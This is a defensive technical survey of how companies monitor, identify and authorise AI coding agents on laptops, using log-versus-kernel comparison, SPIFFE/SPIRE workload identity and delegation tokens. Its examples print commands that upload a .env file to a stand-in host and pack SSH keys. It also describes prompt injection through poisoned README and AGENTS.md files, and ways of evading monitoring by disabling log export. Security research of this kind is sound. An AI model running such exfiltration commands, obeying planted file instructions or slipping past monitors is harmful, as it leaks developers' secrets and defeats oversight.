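AgentSight slowed Claude Code by an average of 2.9 percent on three programming tasks, with a range of 0.4 to 4.9 percent. The researchers ran each task only three times with the monitor and three times without, so some of the difference may be due to chance. The slowdown still seems small enough for everyday use.

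### Three commands on one laptop

Suppose a company exports full commands and prompts from its approved coding agent, and the endpoint monitor on a developer's laptop records these three commands.

| Command | What started it | Entry in the agent's log | Prompt for that session |
|---|---|---|---|
| `npm test` | The approved agent | Same command, same second | "Fix the failing login test" |
| `curl -F file=@.env https://build-check.example` | The approved agent | Same command, same second | "Get this project to build" |
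| `tar czf /tmp/k.tgz ~/.ssh` | A second copy of the agent, which a script started with its export switched off | None | No session |

The test run needs no further attention, because the developer asked for a fix and the agent ran the tests.

By comparing the two records, the analyst can see that an agent ran the `tar` command that packs up the developer's SSH keys, and that the company has no session for that agent. This doesn't require reading any prompts. The explanation could still be harmless, such as a failed export, but the missing session is worth investigating.

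This works only because the company can recognise the process as an agent that should be reporting. Developers and ordinary programs also run commands without an agent, so alerting on every command without a log entry would flag most of the activity on the laptop. If the intruder had used a home-made script, the company would first have to recognise it as an agent, which is the problem Canale and Soulis' detector is meant to solve.

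The `curl` command is harder to judge because the agent's log entry matches the machine's record. The command uploads .env, a file that often holds access keys, so somebody has to decide whether building the project requires the upload. Most builds don't, but some do send settings to an outside service.

The analyst therefore needs to know where the agent got the address. In this example, it came from a poisoned README. Claude Code can export the contents of files it reads, but only if tracing and another setting are turned on. AgentSight would have the text anyway, because the agent passes it to the model. If the address appears in the README but not in the prompt, that suggests the file caused the upload. But people also put genuine instructions in README files, so the analyst still needs evidence that the developer authorised the upload, such as a signed delegation record.

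The comparison might also come too late. Claude Code logs a tool's result only after the tool finishes, and AgentSight's second model runs in the background while the agent continues, so the keys would probably be stolen before anyone saw the alert.

An attacker who prompts the approved agent directly may leave no mismatch between the agent's log and the machine's record. In the Nx attack, the malware told agents to search for sensitive files, and some did. That request would have fully explained the search. The same would be true of the `tar` command if the company had prevented anyone from switching off the export. The intruder's session would then appear in the log, along with a prompt asking for the keys. The prompt might look suspicious, but comparing the two records can't establish who wrote it.

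### Following an action through files

AgentSight can lose track of an action that happens much later. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an attacker who has an agent write a malicious script and schedule it with cron, the Linux scheduler. An hour later, cron runs the script, which gives the attacker a command shell. By then the half-second window has closed, and the script's process isn't descended from the agent.

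AgentLoupe solves this by attaching a label to each exchange with the model. The programs a process starts and the files it writes inherit its label, as does any process that later opens those files. In a test of the cron attack, the label linked the attacker's shell to the original request. In another test, one session planted an instruction in AGENTS.md and a later session followed it, and AgentLoupe linked the two sessions through the file.

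The extra tracking slowed three tasks by 4.5 to 8 percent, compared with 1.7 to 4.5 percent for AgentSight on the same machine. Labels can also spread too far, for example when many programs read the same file. Bao and colleagues have not measured how often the labels create false links or miss real ones.

*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) tracks processes and files in a similar way without reading model traffic. The monitor slowed the test workloads by 0.2 to 3.5 percent. It could show that a scheduled script came from an agent, but not which request led to the script.

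### How much the two records add to each other

King, Zhang and colleagues ran the largest test of combining the records in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (2026). They collected 4,047 sessions of Claude Code's command-line agent running in containers and gave ten detectors the application's records, the kernel's records or both. As in Sophos' test of its command classifier, the scores measure how well a detector ranks malicious sessions above harmless ones, so 0.5 is no better than chance.

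Seven of the ten detectors did best with both records when tested on types of attack they had not trained on. The score for XGBoost, a common classifier, rose from 0.750 with the better single record to 0.850 with both.

Averages across the detectors, this time on familiar types of attack, show why the combination helps:

| Attack | Application records | Kernel records | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copying credentials into a log file | 0.586 | 0.976 | 0.970 |
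| Planting a misleading reference in retrieved text | 0.906 | 0.703 | 0.927 |

The credential theft never appeared in the transcript, but the misleading reference changed only text and left little trace in the kernel. These detectors looked for patterns in whole sessions and did not match individual entries to actions, so their scores are better evidence for collecting both records than for any particular way of matching them.

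In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested matching each agent's own log, entry by entry, against a separate record of its model traffic, processes and file changes. They altered copies of the logs by removing, changing or inventing one item. Using rules fixed in advance, they found 64 of 66 alterations and wrongly flagged none of 84 unaltered logs. In an earlier test without the separate record, the AI reader with the fewest false alarms noticed 49 percent of the altered logs and wrongly suspected 5 percent of the unaltered ones.

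That is very strong evidence for finding false logs. It doesn't help with the `curl` command, whose log entry is true.

### Can someone falsify the agent's log?

An attacker with access to the developer's account may be able to edit a log stored there. The usual defense is to send each entry to another machine immediately, so that nobody on the laptop can change it later. This is worth doing, but it can't guarantee that the entry was true or that the agent sent one at all.

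Dai and colleagues showed the same weakness in a hash chain, which links each entry to the previous one so that later edits can be detected. They modified a coding agent to leave out or invent messages in 28 runs. The chain passed its check every time because nobody had changed the entries after the agent wrote them.

The risk to an agent's log depends on the attack. A poisoned file influences what the model does, but the program that writes the log is still genuine and will normally record the resulting commands. An attacker who can replace that program or change its settings is a greater danger to the log.

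Companies can lock some of those settings. In Claude Code, a central setting can force logs to go to the company's server, but the company has to lock the on/off switch for log export separately. Otherwise, Anthropic warns, a settings file in a downloaded project can turn the export off. An attacker could put that file in the same project as the poisoned README. The endpoint monitor would then record an agent that had sent the company no log.

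A kernel monitor is harder for an ordinary program to avoid, but an attacker with kernel-level privileges could interfere with it. Cui and colleagues therefore assume that the attacker has no such privileges. The model provider's copies of model calls are a useful further check. Dai and colleagues retrieved the provider's copies of 708 calls, and all of them matched their separate record exactly.

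### Busy agents and missing entries

Time is a poor way to match records on a busy machine. If unrelated programs start at random, averaging *r* per second, the chance that at least one starts within a window of *w* seconds is 1 − e^(−*rw*). With two starts a second and a half-second window, the chance is 63 percent. A large software build might start 20 programs a second, which would put an average of ten unrelated programs in that window.

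Process ancestry and matching text rule out many false matches between the agent's log and the machine's record, but several agents may be running similar commands at once. Zheng and colleagues monitored six agents working on one project and still had 3,153 events after merging.

Theodoro (2026), in *Estimating the agent actions that no log recorded*, used the overlap between several incomplete logs to estimate how many actions all of them had missed. On infrastructure tasks, his 95 percent intervals contained the true number in about 95 percent of simulated trials when he matched entries by an exact identifier. When he matched them by what the action did, the figure fell to 40 percent, because different actions with the same effect looked like one action.

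An agent's log also loses detail when the agent puts many steps in one script. When Theodoro gave an agent a tool for running scripts, it carried out 86 percent of its 1,283 actions that way, and its log held one entry for each script. An entry such as `python setup.py` could account for hundreds of file changes and an upload. An analyst has to check what the script did on the machine, not just whether the agent's log has an entry for its launch.

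Running each agent session in its own container makes it much easier to match the agent's log with the machine's record. King and colleagues ran 30 sessions this way, three at a time, and found none of the 8,240 recorded events in the wrong session's trace. Their method doesn't cover agents built into code editors or desktop apps, which many developers use.

### When a model judges the match

A company with thousands of sessions a day would probably want a model to judge whether each request explains the agent's actions. In King and colleagues' test on unfamiliar types of attack, one general-purpose model, Qwen3-80B, scored 0.810 when given both the agent's log and the machine's record, meaning it ranked a harmless session as more suspicious than a malicious one about 19 percent of the time. Stronger models may do better, but real attacks are so rare that most of even a good model's alarms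 could be false.

Legitimate agents also do things nobody requested, as the overeagerness tests by Qu and colleagues showed. The judge would correctly find that the request did not explain those actions, even though no attacker was involved.

An attacker can also try to manipulate the model that analyses a log. *Agentic Cloud Decoys* (2026) points out that attackers choose some of the text in logs, such as file names, and that the model may follow instructions hidden there. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) cites an experiment in which planted log data led AI agents to compromise the systems they managed. Cleaning the data before the agents read it blocked those attacks.

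Matching is safer when fixed rules do as much of it as possible. For example, a rule could flag any upload to an address that appears in a file the agent read but not in the user's prompt. That would catch the `curl` command without using a model to infer what the developer meant, although it would also flag uploads that follow genuine instructions in a README.

### The privacy cost of collecting prompts

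Developers paste customer records, unreleased code and passwords into prompts, and some ask personal questions. A central store of prompts is therefore a serious privacy risk and an attractive target for thieves. AgentSight collects this material by design, because it reads the agent's decrypted model traffic.

Exported logs give a company more choice, but the settings are easy to get wrong. Turning on prompt logging in Claude Code also logs the text of the model's replies, unless the company disables that separately. Full commands can contain passwords, as they did in Elastic's Mac session. According to Coralogix, a prompt passed to Gemini CLI in its launch command appears in the exported data even when prompt logging is off.

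A company can avoid collecting most prompts. Session and command records are enough to notice the `tar` command, and analysts need the prompt only for actions like the `curl` upload. The company could export commands routinely and let analysts open a prompt only when a command looks dangerous.

The full prompts still have to be stored somewhere. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* recommends that logs hold identifiers, hashes and pointers to the full content, mainly because logging everything is expensive. If the full content stays on the laptop, an intruder can delete it, and Claude Code itself deletes old transcripts after 30 days by default. A hash stored elsewhere would reveal that somebody had changed a prompt, but nobody could recover a deleted prompt from it. Copying the prompts to a restricted store off the laptop would preserve the evidence, but the company would then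 be holding the prompts after all.

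## Workload identity and attestation: proving what a process is

In the log comparison, an analyst could investigate the `tar` command only because the company recognised the process as one of its agents. A program's name or location is weak evidence of that, since an attacker can copy either. A workload identity is stronger evidence. It is a cryptographic credential that a company issues to a running program, not to a person, after checking what the program is and which machine it is on. Services can then require the credential before accepting a request.

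### How a program gets its credential

SPIFFE is an open standard for these credentials, and SPIRE is software that implements it. A company runs a central SPIRE server and a small helper program on every machine. (SPIRE calls the helper an agent, but it has nothing to do with AI.) An administrator registers each program that should have an identity by listing the properties its process must have. According to SPIFFE's *SPIRE Concepts*, SPIRE then works roughly like this:

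1. The helper proves to the server which machine it is on. In a cloud, it can present an identity document from the cloud provider. On a company's own machine, it can use a private key in a security chip, or a one-time token that an administrator supplied during installation.
2. The server sends the helper the registrations that apply to that machine. The helper obtains the matching credentials in advance and keeps them ready.
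3. A program asks the helper for a credential. It doesn't supply a password or even a name.
4. The helper asks the operating system's kernel which process made the request, then looks up that process's properties.
5. If the properties match a registration, the helper hands over the credential.

Because the program needs no password, there is none in a settings file for malware to find.

The credential is usually a private key and a certificate containing a name such as `spiffe://acme.com/billing/payments`. *SPIFFE/SPIRE Security Self-assessment* (Vega, 2020) gives a default lifetime of one hour. When the program connects to a service, each side presents its certificate and proves that it holds the matching key. This exchange, called mutual TLS, lets the service refuse any program without an acceptable certificate. SPIRE only establishes the program's name, so the service has to decide what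 a program with that name may do.

In Vega's example, a payment program gets its name only if it runs on a cloud machine in a particular security group, in the right part of the company's container system, under the right service account and from a specific container image. Those conditions are quite informative on a server, where an automated system normally starts every program, but the helper has less to check on a laptop, where people start programs by hand.

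CNCFStack's *Agent plugin*, a copy of SPIRE's documentation for Linux and similar systems, lists the basic properties of a process: its user and group and, if an administrator turns this on, the path and SHA-256 hash of its program file. The helper needs extra permissions to look up the path and hash for other users' processes. None of these properties shows what started the process or what somebody asked it to do, which were the two differences between the developer's run and the attacker's run on the imaginary laptop.

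### Remote attestation and the security chip

SPIRE's checks are a form of attestation, in which one party checks evidence about another party's software and machine. *RFC 9334*, an internet architecture document by Birkholz, Thaler and colleagues, defines three main roles. The attester produces evidence about itself. The verifier compares that evidence with a policy and issues a result. The relying party uses the result to decide how to treat the attester. If a laptop asks to join a company network, for example, the laptop is the attester, a company server can be the verifier, and the network equipment that admits or refuses the laptop is the relying party.

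A compromised machine could produce false evidence. One solution is for each layer of software to measure the next one before starting it, usually by computing a hash. The laptop's built-in startup code measures the boot loader, the boot loader measures the kernel, and the kernel could then measure an application. If an attacker had altered the kernel, the boot loader's measurement would reveal the change, and the kernel could not have tampered with that measurement because it was not yet running.

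A Trusted Platform Module (TPM) is a security chip that can store these measurements and sign them with a key designed never to leave the chip. Birkholz and colleagues point out that a TPM does not collect evidence itself, so another component has to supply the measurements. The signed evidence therefore covers only what that component measured. Malware that runs under the developer's account changes neither the boot loader nor the kernel, so the laptop can pass a check of both while the malware is running.

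SPIRE's own use of the chip is narrower. SPIFFE's *SPIRE Agent Configuration Reference* lists a check that uses a TPM with a device certificate to establish which machine the helper is on. The check doesn't establish that the machine's kernel is intact, although the helper depends on the kernel for accurate information about processes. An attacker who controlled the kernel could probably obtain every credential registered for that machine, but not those registered only for other machines.

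*Microsoft Expands Windows Security for AI and Enterprise IT* (Noureen, 2026) describes a Microsoft preview feature that combines several protections of the startup process and the kernel into one security state, which a laptop's hardware can attest. A company could refuse laptops that fail the check, but passing it would not show which agent was running.

### A signed file, a running file and an approved instance

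Vendors and security teams often treat three different claims as one.

| Claim | What can support it | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| The vendor published this file | A digital signature | Whether anyone is running it, and for what purpose |
| This process runs that file | The path and hash, as reported by the kernel | Who started it, and what other code it has loaded |
| This process is the approved instance | A launch that only the company's own system could have performed | Whose instructions it is following |

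Code signing supports only the claim about the publisher. HotHardware's *Microsoft Responds To Security Concerns Over Windows 11's Agentic AI Shift* reports Microsoft's principle that agents on Windows must have a signature from a trusted source, which Microsoft or others can revoke or block. This helps against counterfeit agents, but every copy of a genuine agent has the same signature, whoever installed it. Revoking the signature is therefore unsuitable for stopping a single unwanted copy, because it would also affect the copies that companies had approved.

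A matching hash is better evidence because it concerns a particular process, but it covers only the main program file. In the SesameOp case, the intruders made genuine Microsoft utilities load malicious libraries, and the hash of each utility would still have matched. As with allowlisting, a hash rule for an agent written in Python or JavaScript would accept any other script the same user ran with the same interpreter. A company could avoid this by packaging the agent as a single executable or checking a whole container image. It would also have to register a new hash after each update, and coding agents update often.

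To show that a process is the approved instance, a company has to control how the agent starts.

### Four processes on one laptop

Suppose a company has installed SPIRE on a developer's Linux laptop and registered its coding agent, which is a single executable file. The company's code repository and model gateway accept only programs with the coding agent's credential. Four processes ask for it:

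- the sanctioned agent, working on the developer's request
- a second copy of the same signed program, which malware has started under the developer's account, as in the Nx attack
- a home-made Python script that queries a model and runs commands, also under the developer's account
- the sanctioned agent after it has read a poisoned README file and begun to follow the attacker's instructions

Whether each one gets the credential depends on the registration rule.

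| The rule requires | Sanctioned agent | Second copy | Home-made script | Hijacked agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The developer's account | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| The account, path and file hash | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| A particular system service | Yes | No | No | Yes |
| A separate account for the agent | Yes | No | No | Yes |
| An approved container or virtual machine | Yes | Only if the malware can start or enter one | Only if its author can start or enter one | Yes |

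A rule that checks only the account is almost useless here, because everything the developer runs passes. Checking the path and hash as well excludes the script but not the second copy, because the malware started the same file from the same place.

The service rule depends on systemd, which manages background services on most Linux systems. SPIRL's *Linux systemd Workload Attestor* explains that this check identifies a process by the service that manages it, not by its user or program file. If malware starts the agent directly, the new process doesn't belong to the approved service and gets no credential. The rule has to name a service that only an administrator can change, because users can define their own services.

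A separate account has much the same effect. Malware running under the developer's account normally can't start a process as a different user without first gaining higher privileges. Containers are less reliable because many developers have permission to start them. Malware running under such a developer's account could start another container from the approved image, perhaps with its own script inside.

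The hijacked agent can still get a credential under all of these rules, because only its instructions have changed. NHIMG's *Google Vertex AI agents still need cloud neutral authorization* explains that workload identity establishes which agent is acting, but not what it may do on a person's behalf.

The second copy can also become, in effect, a hijacked agent. The developer has to give the agent work, so an agent in a separate account must accept requests from the developer's account. Malware running under the developer's account may be able to send the same requests, and if so, it doesn't need a second copy.

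Isolation still limits the damage. An agent with its own account can't read the developer's SSH keys unless somebody has given it access. An agent in a container can normally open only the folders that the company or developer has shared with it. A virtual machine adds a separate kernel, which makes it harder for the agent to break out. A poisoned README could then no longer make the agent steal the SSH keys, but it could still make the agent upload the project's `.env` file, because the agent needs access to the project.

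### Why refusing programs works better than watching them

A missing credential is poor evidence of an attack when most harmless programs don't have one either. Suppose one process in 10,000 is malicious and has no credential, and 99 percent of the harmless processes have none. Only about one in 9,900 processes without a credential is then malicious, so checking for a credential is hardly better than picking a process at random.

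Now suppose that the company's model gateway requires the credential, and that one request in 10,000 comes from malware that lacks it. Suppose also that 0.1 percent of requests from legitimate agents lack a valid credential, for example because it has expired. About one in 11 refused requests would then be malicious. These figures are illustrative, but that would be a very good rate for a security alert. The gateway would also stop the malicious request even if nobody read the alert.

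The requirement protects only resources behind a service that enforces it. The developer's SSH keys are ordinary files, and Linux normally lets any program running under the developer's account read them. The home-made script could use its own model account, find the keys and send them to the attacker without contacting any service that checks credentials. To prevent this, the company could block unapproved outside connections, or move its most valuable keys into a secret store that releases them only to registered programs. Vega describes access to secret stores as a common use of SPIRE.

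Records of issued credentials are useful too. Teleport's *Workload Attestation* describes a system that logs the properties of each process when it issues a credential. If a path-and-hash rule accepted the malware's second copy, an analyst could see at once from the log that another process had received the agent's identity. The analyst would still need more evidence, such as the parent process, because developers often run several copies of a coding agent at the same time.

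*Microsoft Ignite 2026* (Burgerhout, 2026) describes a preview feature of Intune, Microsoft's device-management service, that checks laptops for unapproved agents. If Intune finds one, it marks the whole laptop as noncompliant, and Microsoft's sign-in system then blocks that laptop from company data. Burgerhout notes that Microsoft hasn't explained how Intune finds agents or what counts as an agent.

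This feature can act only on unapproved agents that it recognises. ThreatRoundup's *Microsoft Wants to Police the AI Agents on Your Windows PCs* (2026) reports that administrators can now find 60 types of local agent on Windows, including Claude Code and Codex. A home-made script probably isn't among them, so the laptop would still count as compliant. A service that requires a credential would refuse the script without needing to recognise it.

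### Stolen credentials

Malware might steal the sanctioned agent's credential instead of asking for its own. Short lifetimes help because a stolen credential stops working when it expires. A one-hour certificate stolen at a random point in its life has half an hour left on average, compared with 12 hours for a one-day certificate. But an automated attack can do a lot in half an hour, and malware that remains on the machine can steal the replacement too.

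SPIRE can also issue tokens, which are pieces of signed text that a program sends with its requests. Anyone who obtains an ordinary token can use it until it expires. Vega therefore recommends certificates wherever possible, since a thief can't use a stolen certificate without its private key.

Another solution is to bind the token to a certificate. Google Cloud's *Agent Identity overview* describes access tokens that work only if the agent proves that it holds the private key for its certificate. For connections beyond Google's gateway, the agent signs a proof for each request, a method called Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP). According to Google Cloud's *Use Agent Identity with Agent Runtime*, a bound token works only in its intended environment, such as a particular container. A thief who found the token in a log could not use it elsewhere.

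An attacker would then try to steal the private key. SPIRE's helper generates this key on the machine and passes it to the program, so malware that can read the program's memory could copy it. A TPM doesn't prevent this if the company uses it only to identify the laptop.

Keeping the program's own key in the TPM would prevent copying. Malware with the same access as the agent might still get the chip to sign requests, but only while it was running on that laptop. This helps the defender considerably, because an EDR product has a chance to record the activity and removing the malware ends the access.

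### What companies can use in 2026

Workload identity for AI agents is much further along on servers than on laptops.

Google Cloud gives each agent on its supported services a SPIFFE name based on the cloud resource that hosts it. It also issues the agent a 24-hour certificate, which it renews automatically. Unlike with Google's older service accounts, programs don't share these identities by default, and developers can't create long-lived keys for them. When an agent acts for a user, the logs record both the agent and the user. Google's platform starts the agents itself, so it has good evidence of which process is the approved instance.

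For companies that run their own container systems, Red Hat's *Zero Trust Workload Identity Manager* documents SPIRE as part of the OpenShift platform. SPIRE works for programs in general, including AI agents.

On laptops, Microsoft has concentrated on isolation. Its *Securing AI agents on Windows* (2025) announced separate Windows accounts for agents and a contained workspace with its own desktop. Its *Experimental Agentic Features* (2025) describes the preview, which is off until an administrator enables it. An agent can ask for access to the user's Documents, Downloads, Desktop, Music, Pictures and Videos folders. SSH keys are normally kept elsewhere, so the agent could not read them, but it could read a planted file in Downloads, where Forever Security found the malicious AGENTS.md.

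In June 2026, Microsoft introduced a more general system, Microsoft Execution Containers. Microsoft's *Windows platform security for AI agents* (2026) describes two main forms:

- Process isolation runs code within the user's own environment but restricts which files and network addresses it can reach. GitHub's command-line Copilot uses it.
- Session isolation gives the agent a separate account and Windows session. Windows attributes everything in that session to the agent's identity, so an analyst can distinguish the agent's actions from the user's.

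Running agents in virtual machines on the laptop was still only planned at that point, but companies could already run them on separate cloud PCs. The containers became generally available in October, according to the announcement *Microsoft Execution Containers*. The announcement also states the principle behind them, that an agent can't be its own security authority. Something outside the agent has to enforce the limits, whatever the model does.

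The arrangement for coding agents is weaker. Microsoft's *Build and run agents locally on Windows* says that a coding agent directed by a developer runs in the developer's own session. Windows can tag the agent's processes, but Microsoft still describes distinguishing an agent's actions from a person's as a future feature of Entra, its identity service. A tag would help an analyst separate Claude Code's commands from those the developer typed, but if malware started a second copy of the agent, Windows would presumably tag that copy too.

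Microsoft (2026) reports that organisations have registered more than 50 million agents in Agent 365, its management service, since May. A registry entry can record who owns an agent, but it doesn't prove that a particular process on a laptop is that agent.

A company could instead build its own system for laptops with SPIRE, which works on Linux and macOS. SPIFFE's *SPIRE now runs on Windows* (2022) announced Windows support but warned that matching the Linux version would take several releases. The systemd rule in the four-process example would still work only on a Linux laptop.

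### Cost, old services and lock-in

Running SPIRE takes substantial work, because the company has to maintain the servers, install a helper on every machine and keep the registrations up to date. Encryption Consulting warns that if SPIRE is unavailable, every program that depends on it can fail to authenticate. The SPIRE server is also an attractive target, because an attacker who controls its database could register malicious programs as legitimate ones.

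A company can reduce the risk of an outage by running several servers. The helpers also keep copies of credentials, so programs can keep working through a short outage until those credentials expire. Longer-lasting credentials allow more time for repairs but give a thief more time to use a stolen one. For agents that already run in one company's cloud, a managed service such as Google's avoids most of this work.

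Many outside services accept only an API key or a password, so an agent can't log in to them directly with a workload identity. Google handles this with a broker that holds the keys for those services. The agent authenticates to the broker with its SPIFFE identity. In some set-ups, a gateway adds the user's credential to the request, so the agent never has it. SPIRE users can put a proxy in front of an old internal service for a similar purpose. Both methods keep secrets away from the agent, but an outside service that accepts an API key will accept it from anyone, so a thief who gets the key some other way can bypass the broker.

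Descope, which sells a competing product, praises Google's agent identities for agents on Google Cloud but objects that Google also controls the system for managing them. The use of SPIFFE partly answers this objection, since other companies' software can verify a SPIFFE credential. Microsoft's *Google Cloud Federation*, a technical reference from April 2026, explains how to exchange a Google Cloud program's identity for access through Entra. That makes the agent's identity portable, but a company that moved to another cloud would still have to rebuild its permissions and its store of outside credentials.

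### Malware under the developer's account

The most serious objection is that malware on a laptop usually runs under the developer's account, so it can start the same programs as the developer. This objection is correct for the simpler rules in the four-process example. A company that registers its coding agent by user, path and hash will exclude home-made scripts, but it will give malware a credential whenever the malware starts the real agent.

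A separate account or a managed service closes that route, but the agent then loses automatic access to the developer's files, tools and logins, which are much of what makes it useful. Microsoft recommends process isolation for coding agents because developers need them to respond quickly, but warns that this form of isolation may be too limiting for heavier workloads.

Malware could still send requests to the isolated agent. The company could require the developer to approve sensitive actions on a phone or a hardware key, which malware on the laptop can't operate. Developers would tolerate this for publishing a package or reading a production password, but not for every command.

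Automated builds are an easier place to start. Nobody needs to share an account with the agent there, and the build system can start each job in a fresh container with its own credential. The company can also decide in advance which services the job needs and have all the others refuse it.

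## Delegation records: proving who authorised an action

A workload identity can prove that a process is the company's approved coding agent, but not that anyone at the company asked for what the agent is doing. A delegation record is meant to prove this with a verifiable statement of who authorised the agent, what they authorised it to do, and for how long.

Many agents on laptops have no delegation records. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a post about agent identity, describes how people share their passwords with agents or run agents under their own accounts, so the agents' requests appear to come from the person. NIST warns that this undermines non-repudiation, the ability to prove afterwards who carried out an action. It wants each agent to have its own identifier, credentials and permissions, tied to the user or system that operates it.

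### One repository for one hour

Suppose a developer named Dana wants a coding agent to review her team's login code. At 2 pm, she lets it read one repository for an hour. The company's authorisation server, which issues permissions, signs a record of her permission. The last column gives the usual field names in JSON Web Tokens, a common format for such records.

| What the record holds | In this example | Field |
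|---|---|---|
| Issuer | The company's authorisation server | `iss` |
| Person | Dana | `sub` |
| Agent | Coding agent, session 7 | `act` |
| Service | The company's code repository service | `aud` |
| Scope | Read the repository shop/login | `scope` |
| Expiry | 3 pm | `exp` |
| Agent's key | A fingerprint of the agent's public key | `cnf` |

The agent sends the record with each request, and the repository service makes four checks:

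1. The signature is genuine, so nobody has altered the record since the authorisation server issued it.
2. The record is for this service and has not expired.
3. The agent has signed the request with the private key that matches the fingerprint. A thief who has copied only the record fails here.
4. The scope covers the requested action.

The service can do all of this without contacting Dana or the authorisation server. But if Dana withdraws her permission at 2:15, the service will keep accepting the delegation record unless someone notifies it. A short expiry limits how long this can continue.

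The afternoon's log might look like this:

| Time | What the agent did | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 2:03 | Read a file in shop/login | Allowed |
| 2:21 | Tried to save a change to shop/login | Refused, outside the scope |
| 2:22 | Asked for permission to save changes, "to submit the fix" | Dana approved it for 15 minutes |
| 2:24 | Saved the change | Allowed under the second record |
| 2:31 | Tried to read shop/payments | Refused, outside the scope |
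| 3:05 | Tried to read shop/login again | Refused, expired |

An analyst would ask about the attempt at 2:31. It could be innocent, because the payment code may depend on the login code. Either way, the analyst knows which agent made the attempt, whose task it was working on, and what Dana had approved by then. If the agent had used Dana's own account, the log would show only Dana opening a repository she is entitled to open.

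### How much of this OAuth already does

OAuth 2.0, the standard behind the screens that ask whether an app may read someone's calendar, already lets a person give software limited permission that expires. NIST notes that companies can now issue short-lived tokens with narrow permissions for a single service. Google already uses the key check in the example for its agents, through a method called proof of possession.

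Traditional OAuth scopes are coarse, so an agent that needs one repository may get access to all of them. NIST mentions two newer specifications that would help. Rich Authorization Requests can describe a permission much more precisely. Transaction Tokens are meant to carry the details of an authorisation along a chain of people and agents, with the permission shrinking at each step. If Dana's agent asked a helper agent to check one folder, the helper should get access only to that folder.

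OAuth is weaker at identifying the agent. Hardt (2026) points out in *AAuth Protocol* that each service issues its own identifiers for the apps that use it, so GitHub doesn't recognise an identifier issued by Google. It may also be unclear what an identifier refers to. In *What Exactly Are We Identifying When We Identify an AI Agent?*, Flanagan (2026) reports that participants at the November 2026 meeting of the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF 127), an internet standards body, distinguished between the identity of a piece of software and the identity of one running instance.

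A defender needs a record of who authorised an action. If every copy of a coding agent has the same identifier, the defender can't use a record that names only the software to tell a user's session from a copy that malware has started.

Tobin South and colleagues have proposed a research framework for "authenticated, authorized, and auditable" delegation to agents. In Dana's case, the service would have to identify the agent, the agent would have to stay within its permission, and somebody would have to be able to trace its actions afterwards. Current proposals for achieving this differ mainly in how much new infrastructure they would require.

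### Combining existing standards

The most cautious proposal is the Agent Identity Management System (AIMS). In *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues (2026) describe how to apply or extend existing standards without defining a new protocol. They treat an agent as a kind of workload, so the identity methods companies already use for servers also apply to agents. The group includes employees of Amazon's cloud business, OpenAI and Okta.

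IDPro's *Assembly Required*, written by people who worked on the project it describes, argues that the industry has "an assembly gap" because the necessary standards exist but new agent proposals keep reinventing them. The argument is persuasive for a company's own systems, where the same team can configure every part.

AIMS has also gone furthest at the IETF, where the working group on workload identity has adopted the draft and continues to develop it under a new name. However, it is a guide to best practice, so a monitor that followed it would check tokens from the underlying standards. Those checks could expose a program with no valid permission, but they would add no new evidence about a hijacked agent.

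### Two proposals named AAuth

Two unrelated proposals are called AAuth. Dick Hardt's would be a new protocol in which every running agent has its own identifier and signs every request with its own key. A service can verify the signature even if it has never dealt with the agent before.

Hardt also adds a person server, which represents the user or organisation the agent works for. It handles consent and records what the agent did. If the server requires closer supervision, the agent must propose a mission, which describes the task and lists tools, for the person to approve. The server then logs the agent's requests for access and permission during that mission, along with any questions the person asks and the agent's answers. It can compare each new request with the mission and the earlier entries.

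This is the most useful proposal for a monitor because it preserves evidence of what the person wanted. In the comparison of an agent's log with the machine's record, an intruder who prompted the approved agent left a log that looked like the developer's own work. With a mission, the intruder would also need the developer to approve the task. A developer asked to approve "find all access keys in the home folder" has a good chance of noticing something is wrong.

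The evidence would be on the person server, however, and the service would often have much less of it. In three of the five ways Hardt describes for a service to handle access, the service is told which person the agent acts for, and sometimes what that person agreed to, but never receives the agent's identifier. An employer would therefore need to run the person server, or have access to its log, to find out which agent made a request.

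The protocol also depends on the organisation that issues the agent's identity. Hardt leaves the check before issuing to a mechanism specific to each platform. If that check accepts any copy of the right program under the developer's account, malware could obtain an identity for a second copy, though that copy still wouldn't have an approved mission.

The other AAuth, by Jonathan Rosenberg and Pat White, would extend OAuth instead of replacing it. In White's earlier draft, also called *AAuth* (May 2025), an agent asks for authorisation, waits for an answer, and then receives a token, which lasts 15 minutes in White's example. A monitor could use the request and the answer, much like the 2:22 entry in Dana's log, to establish that somebody approved the new permission after the agent asked for it.

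Neither AAuth protocol is a standard. Hardt's September 2026 version is an individual draft, which anyone may submit to the IETF, and it expires in March 2027 unless he updates it. According to Flanagan's *Do We Need New Protocols, or Better Architecture?* (2026), the draft is now an input to work at the OpenID Foundation, which maintains a widely used standard for signing in.

### Delegation between organisations

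A company can tell its own services which authorisation server to trust, but this is harder when the agent belongs to a customer or supplier. Hardt's design and KYA-OS (Know Your Agent Operating System) are both partly responses to this problem. The Decentralized Identity Foundation's *DIF and Vouched Advance Agentic Identity with KYA-OS* (2026) describes delegation credentials that state their scope, reveal tampering, and work between organisations with no prior arrangement.

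KYA-OS has three levels. The first uses existing tokens, the second adds full delegation credentials and a way to revoke them, and the third adds permanent audit records. The second level seems like the sensible minimum for security, since a company that discovers a hijacked agent needs to be able to cancel its permission. The Foundation is still developing the specification with its members.

IETF 127 also had a session on Agent Use of Delegation and Interaction Traceability (AUDIT). It was a "Birds of a Feather" session, which the IETF uses to explore possible new areas of work, not to set standards. Traceability would help an analyst investigate a chain of agents. If Dana's agent starts a helper and the helper calls an outside service, the service's log may show only the helper.

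### A hijacked agent with a valid record

Delegation records work well against a program that has no right to be there, but much less well when an attacker has hijacked the agent that holds the record. Suppose an attacker has planted an instruction in the README of the repository in Dana's example, telling the agent to copy the source code, including an access key somebody left in a settings file, to `build-check.example`.

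| Situation | Result at the repository service |
|---|---|
| Malware starts a second copy of the agent, with no record | Refused |
| Malware copies Dana's record but not the agent's private key | Refused |
| The hijacked agent tries to read shop/payments | Refused |
| The hijacked agent reads shop/login, then uploads it to the attacker | Reading allowed |

In the last case, the signature is valid, the hour has not run out, and Dana did authorise the agent to read that repository, so the service should allow the read. The service has no record of the upload, because the agent sends the files directly to the attacker's server, which does not check whether Dana permitted it.

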